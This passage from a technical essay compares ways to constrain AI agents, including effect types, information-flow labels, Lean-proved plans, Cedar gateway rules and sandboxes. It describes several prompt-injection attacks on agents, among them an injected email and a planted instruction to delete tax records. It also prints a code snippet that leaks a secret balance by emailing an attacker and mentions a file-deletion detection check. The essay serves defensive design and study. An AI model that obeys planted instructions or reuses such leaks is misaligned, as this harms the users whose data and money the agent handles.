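A program of type `BankIO ()` can combine these three functions with any amount of pure computation. It can't write a file, because the function for that returns an `IO` action. If it calls another agent, that agent's code must also have type `BankIO`, so delegation can't widen its permissions.

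`Approved` partly answers the objection about coarse effects. `BankIO` alone would allow any payment, but `transfer` accepts only an `Approved Payment`, which an agent can get only from `askUser`. The approved value includes the amount and the payee, so the agent can't get approval for $340 and then pay $34,000. It could still use the same approval twice, as in Marron's contract. Linear types, which can require a program to use a value exactly once, would prevent this, and Zhou and colleagues mention single-use authorisations as a possible extension. As in Scala, the protection depends on `askUser` actually asking the user.

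The bibliography agent gives the clearest test of the types themselves. It can write only entries that come from DBLP, a database of computer science publications, because the function that writes to the file accepts only `Trusted` values and only the database lookup produces them. In 100 tasks with Claude Sonnet 5, none of its 925 citations had a wrong author, year or identifier. An ordinary agent with web search got 19 of 1,002 wrong. The type guarantees only where an entry came from, so a correctly copied citation may still be irrelevant to the topic.

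Recent models seem able to write the necessary Haskell. In ELBA's runs on AgentDojo with four models from Anthropic and OpenAI, type errors caused an average of 0.13 retries per run, and only 7 of 2,688 runs failed because a model never produced a well-typed program.

### Tracking data while the program runs

Sometimes a program's data can't be identified as trustworthy or untrustworthy until the program runs. For such cases, ELBA uses LIO, an existing Haskell library that labels data with its sources. A type marks the computations that LIO controls, but LIO checks the labels at run time. For example, if a program reads a page from an untrusted website and then tries to write to a destination that requires trusted data, LIO stops it with an error.

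ELBA's most striking safety result comes from this part of the system, so it is evidence for tracking data but provides little evidence about type checking. On AgentDojo's tasks for the messaging service Slack, all four models resisted every attack even with the rules switched off. The team therefore simulated a worst case in which an agent obeys any attacker's text it reads. ELBA withstood the attack in all 735 runs per model with the rules on, compared with 425 to 621 with them off. But the rules also blocked legitimate work, and the number of tasks completed per model fell from 494–558 to 294–351.

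In *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) track data flow at run time instead of using static types. In their small language, LLMbda, every value carries a label that the interpreter updates at each step. They proved, with the proof checker Lean, that data with a restricted label can't influence results it shouldn't reach, except through whether the program finishes. An explicit command can lift the restriction, but an auditor can at least look for that command. On AgentDojo's banking tasks, their agent resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks.

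Garby and colleagues wanted a proof because tracking data at run time is easy to get wrong. They found a leak in CaMeL that looks roughly like this:

```python
rich = True
tmp = True
if account.balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email(attacker, "rich!")
```

The balance is secret, so CaMeL would block an email sent directly from the first `if`. Here, when the balance is high, `tmp` becomes false and CaMeL marks it as secret. The program then skips the line `rich = False`, so CaMeL never marks `rich` as secret and lets the email through.

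A static checker has an advantage with this kind of leak because it examines both branches, including the one that a given run skips. In TACIT, a script can compare a classified balance with a threshold only inside `map`, where it cannot send an email, and the result stays classified. But the compiler may also reject a program whose forbidden branch would never have run.

### Order and dry runs in ETAS

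A set of effects has no order. A script that pays the plumber and then asks for approval has the same effects as one that asks first. Tan, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *ETAS*, present a new language for agents whose typing judgement has one more part:

Γ ⊢ *e* : *τ* ! *ε* ▷ *A*

*A* summarises the sequences of requests that the program may make. In ETAS a program doesn't perform an outside operation itself but requests it, and other code decides how to carry it out. Adapted from Tan and colleagues' example, in which a person approves changes to software, the payment could look like this:

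```
spec AskFirst = Approval.request >> Bank.pay;

flow pay(p: Payment) → unit
    ![Approval.request, Bank.pay] ~ AskFirst {
  if perform Approval.request(p) {
    perform Bank.pay(p);
  }
}

let DryRun = handler { Bank.pay(p) ⇒ { resume; } };
```

The list after `!` is the effect bound, *ε*. The compiler rejects the function if its body could send any other kind of request to the outside world. A caller's bound has to cover the functions it calls, so a function can't hide an effect by delegating it. Tan and colleagues cite a bug report about Goose, a coding agent. According to the report, the user had required approval for sensitive tools, but an agent started by the first one ran such a tool without asking.

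The line `spec AskFirst` sets the order: a program must request approval before its first payment. For `pay`, the compiler derives

*A* = Approval.request ; (1 ⊔ Bank.pay)

which means a request for approval followed by either nothing or a payment. It turns the rule into a small state machine and follows every sequence in *A* through it. If all of them obey the rule, as they do here, the compiler has proved that the function complies. If all of them break it, the compiler rejects the function. If some obey and some don't, for example because one branch asks first and another pays first, the program may run, but the state machine runs alongside it and stops the first forbidden request. In that last case ETAS gives up the all-or-nothing protection of a check in advance, since the program may already have done other things.

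`DryRun` is an example of scoped interpretation. If a developer writes `pay(p) with DryRun`, the payment request goes to the handler, which does nothing and lets the program continue, so the same code can run as a rehearsal or for real. The payment disappears from *ε*, because no request reaches the bank, but it stays in *A*. Most effect systems would keep no record of it, and a function that pays without asking would then look harmless in a dry run. ETAS still applies the rule to that function.

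However, `AskFirst` is a weak rule. It requires asking for approval but not getting it, which is why the code needs an `if`. A single request also satisfies it for any number of later payments to any payee. Marron's event log is stricter because it records which amount and payee the user approved. ETAS leaves such details to the host, the program that carries out requests. The host checks the actual arguments and the user's consent at run time. So a check outside the effect type again answers the objection about coarse effects.

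Tan and colleagues proved that programs keep to their bounds and rules, assuming that every outside operation goes through the host and that the host reports everything it does. One incident they cite shows what can happen when a program's environment doesn't match its description. Evaluators had told Claude Mythos 5 that it was working in an offline simulation, but a configuration error had left the internet reachable, and the model published a malicious software package that affected other people. A type that listed only simulated operations would not have cut off the model's internet access.

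The safety tests were small. Tan and colleagues wrote a coding agent in ETAS and used 10 scenarios with scripted model replies to test the part that decides which files to read. It finished four and refused to continue in six, as intended. The compiler was also tested on six short programs. It accepted the two valid ones and rejected the four with deliberate violations, such as a payment-like request before approval. These results show that the checks work on simple cases, but nobody has yet tested them against an attacker or measured how often they stop a real agent from doing harm.

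The paper's larger gains are in speed, token use and accuracy. The compiler can identify steps that have no side effects and rearrange them, which cut the interpreter's running time by 23.2% on 26 synthetic workflows, excluding time spent waiting for a language model, usually the slowest part of an agent. Trimming old messages, unneeded tools and unused data from the prompts reduced input tokens by 67.8% on 12 workflows. In another experiment, an agent that answers questions about financial reports revised its own code over five rounds, with the compiler checking each version, and its accuracy rose from 69.9% to 78.9%. Tan and colleagues didn't repeat this process with an agent written in another language, so the improvement may have nothing to do with the types.

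## The case for proving a plan safe before it runs

A type checker enforces only rules about what its language was designed to track, such as effects, capabilities or the order of requests. Computer scientist Erik Meijer wants agents to obey any policy that people can state precisely. In his proposal, the model writes its whole plan as a program, along with a mathematical proof that the plan obeys the policy. A separate program checks the proof, and the plan runs only if the proof is correct.

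### Planning before reading

Meijer's *Guardians of the Agents* (2025) starts with a user who asks an agent to fetch and summarise her emails. One email contains a prompt injection that tells the agent to send a summary of the mailbox to an outside address. An agent that makes one tool call at a time may obey it. Meijer has the model write the whole workflow first, as a short JSON program that fetches the emails, summarises them and returns the summary. The model hasn't seen any emails at that point, so they can't add a step to the program. The tool that summarises them may be a language model, but it can't send anything.

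The workflow can still be harmful, because an attacker can also hide instructions in a tool's description. Meijer therefore adds a check between writing the workflow and running it. In the example, the policy forbids any flow of data from `fetch_email` into the body of a `send_email` call whose recipient is outside the company. Existing code-analysis tools can search the workflow for such a flow. Java similarly verifies a program's bytecode before running it.

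In a June 2026 talk, *I've never seen anything scarier than an LLM with tool calls*, Meijer made the argument with types. A plain chatbot is a function of type `Question → Answer`. Tools turn it into `Question → IO Answer`, where `IO` has the same meaning as in Haskell. Such an agent can delete a user's files and then return a polite answer, so checking the answer isn't enough. Claude Code had deleted one of Meijer's files while Meijer was preparing the slides. Meijer thinks nobody can formally define what makes a text safe, which is why so many companies ask another language model to judge it. However, "this program never deletes a file" is a precise statement, provided the plan is data that a checker can analyze.

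### A payment plan with its proof

AI Engineer's *Make the Agent Produce a Program Before It Can Act* (2026), a written version of the talk, gives a small example in Lean, which is both a programming language and a proof checker. The example is a plan that reads a file, with a proof that it deletes nothing. Adapted to the plumber's bill, it could look like this:

```lean
structure Request where
  amount : Nat          -- whole dollars
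  payee  : String

inductive Plan where
  | done    : String → Plan
  | balance : (Nat → Plan) → Plan
  | pay     : Nat → String → Plan → Plan

-- The policy
inductive Obeys (r : Request) : Plan → Prop where
  | done (msg : String) : Obeys r (.done msg)
  | balance (next : Nat → Plan)
      (ok : ∀ b, Obeys r (next b)) : Obeys r (.balance next)
  | pay (msg : String) :
      Obeys r (.pay r.amount r.payee (.done msg))

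-- The request that the user approved
def plumber : Request := { amount := 340, payee := "ACC2002" }

-- The model's plan
def payPlumber : Plan :=
  .balance fun b =>
    if b < 340 then .done "Balance too low"
    else .pay 340 "ACC2002" (.done "Paid")

-- The model's proof
theorem payPlumber_ok : Obeys plumber payPlumber := by
  apply Obeys.balance
  intro b
  split
  · exact Obeys.done _
  · exact Obeys.pay _
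```

A `Plan` can end with a message, look up the balance and continue, or make a payment and continue. The policy, `Obeys`, has a rule for each case:

- A plan that just ends is fine.
- A plan that looks up the balance is fine if the rest of it obeys the policy for every balance `b` that the bank might return.
- A payment is fine only if its amount and payee match the request and the plan ends straight afterwards.

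The last rule also prevents a second payment, which Marron's contract and the approved values in Haskell both allowed.

The proof has the same structure as the plan. `intro b` takes an arbitrary balance, and `split` separates the two branches of the `if`. The first branch only returns a message, and the second makes exactly the payment the user requested. If the model had written 34,000 instead of 340, no rule would cover the payment, so no proof could exist.

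The bank or the application's developer writes the policy, and the application creates `plumber` from what the user approved. The model writes the plan and the proof. Lean checks the proof, and an interpreter then carries out the plan step by step.

### What the user still has to trust

Lean's kernel, which *Provably Complete Generalized Planning with LLMs* (2026) describes as a small trusted program, makes the final decision. A model may need a long search and complicated software to find a proof, but nobody has to trust either, because the kernel checks every step of the finished proof. If the proof is faulty, the agent only has to try again. Asking a language model to review the plan doesn't offer this protection because, as the survey *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (2026) points out, a model that produces an unsafe plan can also justify it. Meijer credits the idea of proving a plan safe before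 it runs to proof-carrying code, which researchers developed in the 1990s so that a computer could safely run a stranger's program.

The kernel confirms only that the conclusion follows from the definitions and axioms it has received. *Evidence-Grounded Verified Agentic Reasoning* (2026), which adds the results of tool calls to proofs as axioms, limits its guarantee in the same way. If the model could add axioms, it could assume that its plan obeys the policy, so the application has to fix the statement to be proved and reject extra axioms. The interpreter must also be trusted, because if it paid the plumber twice for every `.pay`, the user would lose $340 even though the proof was valid.

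### Types that mention values

In Lean, the statement `Obeys plumber payPlumber` is a type, and a proof of the statement is a value of that type, so checking a proof is a form of type checking. This requires dependent types, types that can mention values, in this case a particular request and a particular plan.

Dependent types can also link an approval to one payment. The Haskell library ELBA does this by packing the amount and the payee into the approved value. In Lean, the approval's type can name the payment:

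```lean
askUser  : (p : Payment) → BankPlan (Option (Approval p))
transfer : (p : Payment) → Approval p → BankPlan Receipt
```

The type of the second argument to `transfer` depends on the value of the first. An approval for $340 has a different type from an approval for $34,000, so a plan that mixes them up fails the check. The check works even if nobody knows the amount until the plan runs, because both lines refer to the same `p`.

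For this one rule, the Haskell version protects the user just as well. Dependent types become more useful when a rule connects separate values. For example, `transfer` could also require a proof that the amount is no higher than the total on a particular invoice.

### What Lean can prove and an automatic solver can't

*Lean4AgenticRL* (Wang, Friedland and colleagues, 2026) compares Lean with two other formal languages. The paper uses Lean to grade agents' work during training rather than to approve plans, but its comparison applies here too.

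Linear temporal logic (LTL) describes a run as a sequence of steps at which plain facts are true or false. It can state that an approval comes before a payment, but not that the approved and paid amounts are equal. It can also require a test run after every edit an agent makes to a program, as long as several edits may share one test run. Wang and colleagues say LTL can't express this requirement, which is true only if each edit needs its own test run.

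SMT solvers, such as the one behind Marron's checker, handle amounts and comparisons well, but they generally can't prove facts about recursive definitions, because that takes induction. Suppose a plan pays a list of bills and has to stay within a budget. An inductive proof shows that the plan stays within budget for an empty list, and that if it does so for a given list, it still does when one more bill is added. The proof covers lists of every length, whereas Marron's checker covers only lists up to a chosen size.

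The drawback is that somebody has to find the proof. A solver searches for an answer by itself, while Lean has some automation but no general method that works for every true statement. In another talk, *Return of the Theorem* (2026), Meijer proposes an alternative to Lean, using SMT solvers and simple if-then rules to check plans against a company's business rules automatically. Those checks would be enough for the plumber's bill.

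Translating ordinary language into Lean also introduces errors. Wang and colleagues had language models turn agents' written plans into formal conditions, then had Claude Fable 5.1 check 32,295 of these annotations. It judged 8.03% of them wrong, mostly because the original wording was ambiguous. Their training method tolerated this error rate, but a bank could hardly accept a payment policy with one in twelve conditions wrong.

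### Rules from a human-written ontology

*Provably Auditable and Safe LLM Agents from Human-Authored Ontologies* (Sterling, 2026) addresses where the rules come from. A human expert writes an ontology, a structured description of the things, processes and policies in a field, based on an existing template called Basic Formal Ontology. A language model then derives from it the agents' roles, the data each agent may see, and the invariants the system must maintain. Sterling suggests that the expert then follow, for example, a patient through every stage of care and look for forbidden changes that no invariant blocks.

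One of Sterling's two domains is billing for drug tests under Arizona's public health insurance. A patient who has been abstinent for more than 90 days may have three detailed tests in 90 days, but after a relapse the limit is one every seven days. Suppose a patient's detailed test on 23 March is negative. On 26 March, a quick test detects opioids, and the clinic orders another detailed test to confirm the result. A billing agent that still has the patient's old status would wrongly say that the insurance covers this test.

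In Sterling's architecture, Agentic Redux, agents can only propose changes. A central "meta-agent", which is a fixed checklist rather than a language model, sees all the data. It works out what the new state would be, tests every invariant on it, and accepts the change only if all of them pass. The main theorem can be written briefly, with *I* for the invariants:

If *s*₀ satisfies *I*, then every state reachable from *s*₀ satisfies *I*.

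One theorem guarantees that agents sharing a budget can't together exceed it, whatever they propose and in whatever order. If two agents share $100,000, for example, one can't spend $45,000 while the other spends $60,000. A second theorem guarantees that every decision adds exactly one entry to a log that nobody can edit.

So Sterling proves something about the architecture once, and the agents never have to prove anything. This limits the guarantee. Sterling promises correct executions in the paper's abstract, but proves only that the recorded state obeys the written rules, which would be true even if the agents never proposed anything useful. The proof assumes that the rules capture the real regulations and that the software matches the mathematics. A human supervisor can also override an invariant, which voids the guarantee. Sterling says the log contains a proof for each accepted change,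 but in the formal definition, an entry for an accepted change records only an identifier, the time, the action and the verdict.

Sterling provides working code for billing and for disclosing security flaws, but doesn't measure how well the agents do either job. A language model wrote about 90% of the proof appendix. Sterling caught errors in earlier versions and writes that the current proofs "look good to me", a judgement that a proof checker would make unnecessary.

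### Policies that leave something out

Like Marron's checker, all these systems enforce only what somebody wrote down. Meijer gives an example of what a policy can miss. A user asks an agent to delete `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`, and the model writes a shorter plan that deletes `*.txt`, meaning every text file. If the policy requires only that the two files be gone afterwards, this plan passes. Meijer proposes adding a frame condition, which states what must stay the same. But he adds it only to the description of the `delete_file` tool, to say that files outside the pattern survive. The plan that deletes `*.txt` still meets the requirement for the whole task, which covers only the two files. The task needs its own frame condition protecting all other files. If an expert can overlook this in a two-file example, ordinary developers will make similar mistakes.

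Barke and Murali (2026), in *Agents as Software*, describe an email agent that must reply to certain messages. If it reads a message, leaks a password and then replies, it has still obeyed the rule, because the rule doesn't mention passwords. Barke and Murali suggest forbidding everything that the specification doesn't explicitly allow. The `Plan` type above works this way, since it has no operation for sending an email or reading a file. This prevents unforeseen kinds of action, but not the misuse of permitted ones.

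Ciliberto, Rudi and Tassi (2026), in *Proof-Carrying Contracts*, worry that a travel contract might require a flight and a hotel but not matching dates. They propose AI assistants that search for useless outcomes that the contract allows and show these outcomes to the user before the work starts. Nobody has yet measured how many gaps such assistants would find.

Other requirements, such as whether a hotel suits a family, can't be formally defined. For these, Ciliberto and colleagues let the parties appoint an "expert", for example a particular model with a fixed prompt, whose verdict is treated as true. The proof then guarantees that the expert rated the hotel well, but a cleverly written hotel description could still mislead a model acting as the expert.

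### Plans that depend on what a tool returns

Agents often can't know their next step until they see a result. Barke and Murali point out that an agent may revise its plans, its memory and even its code during a run, so there may be no fixed program to check beforehand.

Meijer answers this by putting branches in the plan. The plumber's plan does one thing if the balance is too low and another if it isn't, and the proof covers every possible balance. That works when the model can foresee the kinds of results it might get, but an agent looking for the cause of a server failure can't list every clue it might find.

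A second answer is to plan again. *Soteria* (He, Desai and colleagues, 2026) has a model write a branching plan, which the automatic verifier Dafny checks against formal rules. In conversations with customers, the model writes a new plan after every message. One rule in the paper's airline test is that before cancelling a booking, an agent must confirm that none of its flights has departed. Dafny rejects a plan that skips this check, and the model must then repair the plan.

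Across 207 tasks and four models, Soteria broke none of its rules. However, most of the credit goes to a monitor that also checks each call during the run:

| Rule violations on 50 airline tasks | GPT-5.4-mini | Gemini 3 Flash |
|---|---|---|
| Plan without verification | 13 | 27 |
| Verified plan | 10 | 24 |
| Verified plan built from reusable parts | 12 | 22 |
| The same, with the monitor | 0 | 0 |

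This is weaker evidence against Meijer than it looks. In Soteria, a language model carries out the plan and can depart from it, while Meijer wants an interpreter that follows the plan exactly. Soteria has a strict mode that comes closer to this, but the table doesn't cover it. The zeros also depend on the written rules, some of which He and colleagues corrected or added while auditing the results.

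Soteria increased the share of tasks completed in one setting and reduced it in another. Claude Opus 4.6 completed 88% of the airline tasks with Soteria, compared with 64% without any safeguard, at about two and a half times the cost. On long tasks with files and documents, Opus completed 18.6% with Soteria and 30.2% without safeguards, but more than half of the tasks it completed without safeguards involved a violation.

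The third answer is to give up on proving whole plans. *Proof-Carrying Certificates for LLM Pipelines* (2026) describes an agent that tidies a user's notes by proposing one deletion at a time. A small checked program lets it delete an old draft that belongs to the user and stops it from deleting a shared design document. Ciliberto and colleagues develop this approach furthest. Their agent attaches a Lean proof to every tool call. For a call with input *i* in state *s*, it has to prove:

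∀ *s*′: *D*(*i*, *s*, *s*′) ⇒ *C*(*s*′)

*D* models what the tool could do, and *C* is the contract. Every state the call could lead to must obey the contract, and the agent must prove this for every state *s* that fits what it can currently see.

In one example, an agent may commit at most €2,000 to a trip and may send a passport only to the consulate. An email tells it to send the passport to another address. The system blocks the call because no proof exists that the new address is the consulate's, even though the system doesn't recognise the email as an attack.

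Checking one call at a time doesn't account for later calls. The agent could spend €1,900 on the first two nights, with a valid proof for each booking, and then be unable to afford the third. Checking the whole plan before it runs can catch such problems. Soteria, for example, can verify that a plan that writes a file will always read it back. Ciliberto and colleagues have checked their theory in Lean, but they haven't yet tested whether agents can find the proofs fast enough to be useful.

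### How much somebody has to write

In the Lean example above, the policy takes six lines and the plan takes four. If every plan needed its own policy, people might as well write the plans themselves. Proponents reply that policies can be reused. `Obeys` works for any request, and He and colleagues needed only 24, 33 and 41 formulas for their three benchmarks, spending a few hours on each. A rule about what an agent must never do can also be much shorter than a description of what it should do.

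Besides the policy, people also have to write a formal model of each tool's effects. Ciliberto and colleagues include changes that happen on their own during a call, such as a price increase or a hotel's cancellation. They expect companies to reuse reviewed modules for common operations such as payments.

Meijer argues in the talk that "we should stop designing languages for humans", since machines will write the plans, prove them safe and run them. That is reasonable for the plan and the proof, which the user never needs to read. But someone has to read the policy to judge whether it is right, and `Obeys` is hard to read for anyone who doesn't know Lean.

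## The case for enforcing limits outside the tool description

A Lean proof about a payment plan covers only a formal model of the `transfer` tool, so it stays valid even if the real tool also sends the user's account details to a stranger. Contracts and effect types have the same weakness, because their checkers examine the agent's program and assume the tool's declaration is accurate. Some engineers conclude that safety shouldn't depend on the declaration at all, since it informs the language model but doesn't restrict the tool. They enforce limits in the surrounding system instead, such as in the account's permissions and the network that calls pass through.

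In *Agent Safety is a Box*, Marc Brooker, an engineer who works on agent safety at Amazon Web Services, uses "the box" to mean a layer outside the agent that controls which tools the agent can call and what it can do with them. The box follows fixed rules instead of a model's judgement. Brooker thinks careful prompting and training help agents succeed but can't make them safe, because people use agents for their ability to find approaches nobody planned. If the box allows only one refund per order, and never more than the purchase price, a company knows the most it can lose on an order, whatever an attacker writes in a prompt.

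The blog post *Tool Schemas Are Prompts, Not API Contracts* takes a similar view of descriptions. A developer reads a web service's documentation, writes code, and gets an error if a required field is missing. A model instead rereads the tool description in its prompt at every call and treats the details as suggestions. If a search tool returns 100 results by default, the model takes 100 as the normal number to request. The post therefore recommends writing descriptions for models separately from the OpenAPI documentation, whereas Caldeira wants companies to treat that documentation as the source of truth. The post gives no measurements, and its title is only partly right about schemas, because servers also validate calls against them, though the prose in a description is only a prompt. Faghih, Wang and colleagues found in *Gaming Tool Preferences in Agentic LLMs* (2025) that editing a tool's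 description alone can change how often models choose it.

### How often descriptions and code disagree

Shi, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers*, examined 19,200 tools from 2,214 Python servers. They used a language model to compare each tool's name, schema and prose with its code. Because a model's answer can depend on the wording of the question, they asked it once whether the description and code were consistent and once whether they were inconsistent, then had it resolve any disagreement between the two answers in a third step.

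The model found mismatches in 1,907 tools, which is 9.9% of all the tools and 11.2% of those with a description. 35% of the servers had at least one mismatch. The team then checked 400 of the model's results by hand. Of 200 tools it had flagged, 8 were fine, and of 200 it had passed, 5 had a mismatch. If those error rates hold for the whole collection, closer to 13% of the tools with descriptions have a mismatch, because the model passed far more tools than it flagged.

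Most mismatches are more of a nuisance than a danger. The most common kind, at 35% of cases, is a description that claims something the code can't do. About a quarter involve undeclared side effects. Some of the individual cases are alarming, though:

- According to its description, a tool for placing orders on the MAX exchange asks for the user's explicit approval first. The code submits the order immediately.
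- A tool that is supposed to convert PDF files locally uploads them to an outside service.
- A tool that repeats a message back to the caller adds the server's secret key to its reply.

A description can become inaccurate without an attacker. Shi and colleagues point out that a programmer may change the code and forget to update the description. *Don't believe everything you read* (Li, Ma and colleagues, 2026) examined 10,240 servers and found substantial mismatches between description and code in about 13% of them. That is well below the 35% that Shi and colleagues found, but the paper looked mainly for behaviour that descriptions leave out, while Shi and colleagues also counted exaggerated and vague descriptions.

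### Whether clients can rely on annotations

MCP's annotations could warn a client about hidden behaviour, but they come from the same author as the description. In the project's first discussion of them, MCP's co-creator Spahr-Summers asked how a client could use a flag that it can't trust. The March post on the Model Context Protocol blog acknowledges that a server can set `readOnlyHint` to true and still delete the user's files. It recommends network controls or sandboxing for anyone who needs a guarantee. It also proposes treating any new annotation that is useful only when true as a contract, which the authorisation system or the runtime should enforce. A company that runs its own servers, however, can check their annotations and base rules on them.

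Trofimov and Novikov (2026), in *When Tool Calls Succeed but Workflows Fail*, collected the annotations of 98,291 tools on 4,838 remote servers. Of these tools, 74% set at least one annotation, but a single publisher supplied 45% of the tools, all with the same four fields filled in. Among the remaining tools, 53% set at least one. Only 3.1% of all the tools declare a destructive operation. They did not call any of the tools, so they can't say how many of the annotations are true.

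In *When Neither Side Confirms*, Yao, Yang and colleagues (2026) read the code of 41 popular open-source applications and software kits for building agents to see what each does by default before an ordinary MCP call. In 39 of them, marking a tool as destructive made no difference. Annotations do matter in OpenAI's Codex CLI, which skips its approval prompt for some tools marked as harmless, and in the editor VS Code, which skips it for tools marked read-only, so a false annotation can remove the prompt in either.

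Yao and colleagues also calculated the effect of making every application ask the user about each tool that isn't annotated as read-only or non-destructive. They paired 25 applications with a sample of destructive tools. In 60.7% of these pairs, no approval is enforced now. The change would reduce this to 5.4%, leaving only destructive tools annotated as safe. Across all 41 applications and kits, the figure is at least 10.6% when it includes destructive tools that the team's search had missed. Most annotations therefore aren't dangerously wrong, but too many are for a bank to rely on them. Users would also see many more prompts. For tools that the search wrongly flagged as destructive, the share of pairs that require user approval would rise from 32.5% to 82.6%.

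### How the box handles one payment

Suppose the agent has to pay the plumber $340 from account ACC1001. One place to set limits is the credential, the token that the bank accepts as proof of permission. The bank could issue a token that can debit only this account, up to $500 a day, until midnight. It would then refuse any debit outside those limits, whatever the model writes or the tool's code does with the token.

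Brooker suggests that an agent working for a person should get only a subset of that person's permissions. MCP servers often don't enforce this limit. *Give Them an Inch and They Will Take a Mile* (2026) explains that MCP has no counterpart to Android's central permission system, so every server handles authorisation in its own way. Some servers don't check authorisation at all. Many ask for it once and store the result without tying it to a particular agent, so a second agent that connects to the server could use access that the user granted to the first.

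Another limit can sit between the agent and the tool. In Brooker's design, the agent runs in an environment that blocks every network connection except one to a gateway, a program that receives each call and decides whether to pass it on. The gateway's rules are in Cedar, a language for access policies. Brooker's example limits refunds to less than $500. Adapted to `transfer`, with amounts in whole dollars, the rule might be:

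```
permit(
  principal is AgentCore::OAuthUser,
  action == AgentCore::Action::"BankTool__transfer",
  resource == AgentCore::Gateway::"bank-gateway"
)
when {
  principal.hasTag("username") &&
  principal.getTag("username") == "bill-agent" &&
  context.input.payer == "ACC1001" &&
  context.input.amount < 500
};
```

The first three lines inside the brackets specify who may call which tool through which gateway, and the `when` block adds conditions on the call. The gateway allows the plumber's $340. If the model gives the amount in cents instead of dollars, as 34,000, the gateway rejects the call, even though it is valid under the JSON Schema.

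The rule also has gaps. It allows negative amounts, as Brooker's original does, so the tool's own schema has to exclude them. It checks each call separately, so ten payments of $499 would all pass. Brooker's policy of one refund per order isn't in the sample code, and enforcing it would require a record of earlier refunds.

Even a record may not be enough if the bank's reply gets lost, because the gateway can't determine whether the payment went through. Counting it as paid could leave the plumber unpaid, and allowing another attempt could pay the plumber twice. Trofimov and Novikov argue that no program above the tool can resolve this in general. The tool itself has to provide a means of resolving it, for example a way to look up what happened to an earlier request.

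A third place for a limit is the program that runs the agent's loop. Wang, Poskitt and Sun (2025), in *AGENTSPEC*, present a small language for rules of this kind. Their own example concerns a transfer to somebody called Bob, who may or may not be the user's son. For the plumber, it could become:

```
rule @inspect_transfer
trigger
    Transfer
check
    !is_known_payee
enforce
    user_inspection
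end
```

The trigger is the event that activates the rule, here an attempted transfer. The check is a condition that a programmer writes as an ordinary Python function. The `!` means "not". If the condition is true, the enforcement follows, which in this rule means the agent pauses and asks the user. A rule can also stop the agent, run a different action, or make the model reconsider its plan. Unlike the Cedar rule, this one can respond to a doubtful payment without refusing it.

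The 2025 tests used agents that are now old. Hand-written rules caught more than 90% of the unsafe programs from a coding agent. They also stopped every hazardous action by a robot agent, such as pouring water on a laptop. With the rules in place, the robot agent completed 54.3% of harmless tasks, down from 58.6%. The coding rules were written from descriptions of the same risks used in the tests, so these figures mostly show that the language can express such rules. Rules written by OpenAI's o1, then a leading model, caught 87% of risky code in new cases.

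### Confirmations that the model can give itself

Many tools already have an apparent limit. For example, a tool that deletes files may run only if the call includes `confirm: true`, and its description may say that the user must agree first. Yao and colleagues tested whether this works by having a user ask an agent to delete one note from a list that contained a planted instruction to delete the tax records as well. The server required the flag, but the planted text didn't mention it. Models tried to delete the tax records in 169 runs and succeeded in 127 of them by setting the flag themselves.

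The five models in the test were inexpensive, and one, DeepSeek-V4.1-Flash, never tried to delete the tax records. A stronger model might attempt the deletion less often. But the flag offers no protection, because the model that makes the call also supplies the confirmation.

Real confirmation is rare by default. Yao and colleagues estimate that 90% of destructive tools in MCP's official registry have no server-side confirmation. Of the 41 applications and kits, 32 have no approval step unless somebody turns one on. Developers on each side tend to leave confirmation to the other. One mapping server, according to its instructions, skips confirmation "because MCP clients gate destructive tool calls themselves". Yao and colleagues recommend that developers configure approval in their applications, because the connected tools rarely require a person's confirmation and all 16 software kits in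 the study have approval off by default.

### The outside limits need a notation too

Supporters of typed notations can reply that limits enforced outside the tool description still have to be specified correctly. The Cedar rule and the AgentSpec rule are both formal specifications, and whoever writes them can forget a negative amount or a second payment, just as someone writing a contract can. Brooker admits that most people don't want to learn Cedar, so Amazon's service also accepts rules in ordinary language and translates them, but someone still has to check that the translation matches the intended rule.

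The rules also depend on the tool description. The rule `context.input.amount < 500` works only if the tool has an argument called `amount`, in dollars. Suppose the tool counted in cents, so the limit was set to 50,000, and a later version switched to dollars. The gateway would then allow payments of almost $50,000. If the amount had the type `USD`, as in Marron's contract, a checker could report the mismatch before anyone lost money.

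A small feature of the Model Context Protocol (MCP) shows the same dependence. Its specification lets a tool's author mark an argument so that clients copy it into a header of the web request, where a gateway can read it without parsing the message body. This works for strings, booleans and whole numbers, but not for the type `number`, so the author of `transfer` would have to declare the amount in whole cents. The specification also warns against marking sensitive values, which may include account numbers, because every program that relays the request can read them.

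If outside limits need a specification, the tool's own declaration could supply it. For example, Marron's `permissions` line could be turned into sandbox rules. *AgentBound* (Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues, 2025) does something similar for existing MCP servers. Each server gets a manifest, modelled on Android app permissions, that lists the files, network addresses and secrets it needs. A sandbox runs the server and blocks access to anything not listed, which adds 0.6 milliseconds on average.

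The team's software drafts the manifests from the servers' source code. The team sent 96 drafts to the servers' developers, and those who replied judged 80.9% correct without changes. About one in five of the judged drafts would therefore have given a server too many permissions or too few. Working from the code avoids the problem of false descriptions, but if the code is malicious, the draft may include the permissions that the attack needs, and a person has to notice them.

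Bühler and colleagues give the example of a server for Google Maps that looks harmless but sends its requests to an address other than Google's, which the code spells out as a list of character numbers. A person skimming the code could easily miss this address. A manifest that allows only Google's address would block the connection, whatever the code contains.

### Why a shell defeats a narrow description

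The counterargument is that precise declarations help only with narrow tools. A shell can be described accurately, with a valid schema, as a tool that takes a string and executes it as a command, but its effect type is "anything". Many agents have a shell, and they can use it to bypass the limits on their other tools. If the shell can read the bank's token and reach the bank's network, the agent can make a payment without `transfer`. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) blog warns that a single planted instruction could make an agent with unrestrained shell access leak data, whether or not the shell came through MCP.

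Rules that inspect the command can't reliably stop a coding agent from deleting files. Wang and colleagues suggest an AgentSpec condition that checks the agent's program for a command such as `os.system("rm")`. But Python has other ways to delete a file, and the program could also download a script that does it. A gateway has the same problem, because it receives only a string.

A sandbox and a narrow credential limit what a command can do without having to interpret it. *Securing the Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2025) recommends running every server in a container whose files are read-only except in named folders and whose network access covers only approved addresses. The command then can't delete a file outside those folders or send data to an unapproved address, however the agent words it.

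Bühler and colleagues acknowledge that access control can't prevent misuse within the permitted limits. A tool can still delete everything in the folders where it is allowed to write. A typed interface limits this kind of misuse better, because a tool that can only rename files is safer than a shell confined to the same folder.

### What still holds if the description is false

The approaches differ most when a tool does something its description doesn't mention:

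| Approach | What still holds |
|---|---|
| Better prose, annotations | Nothing |
| JSON Schema validation | The arguments have the declared form |
| Contracts, effect types and proofs about the agent's program | The program follows the declared rules when it calls the tool |
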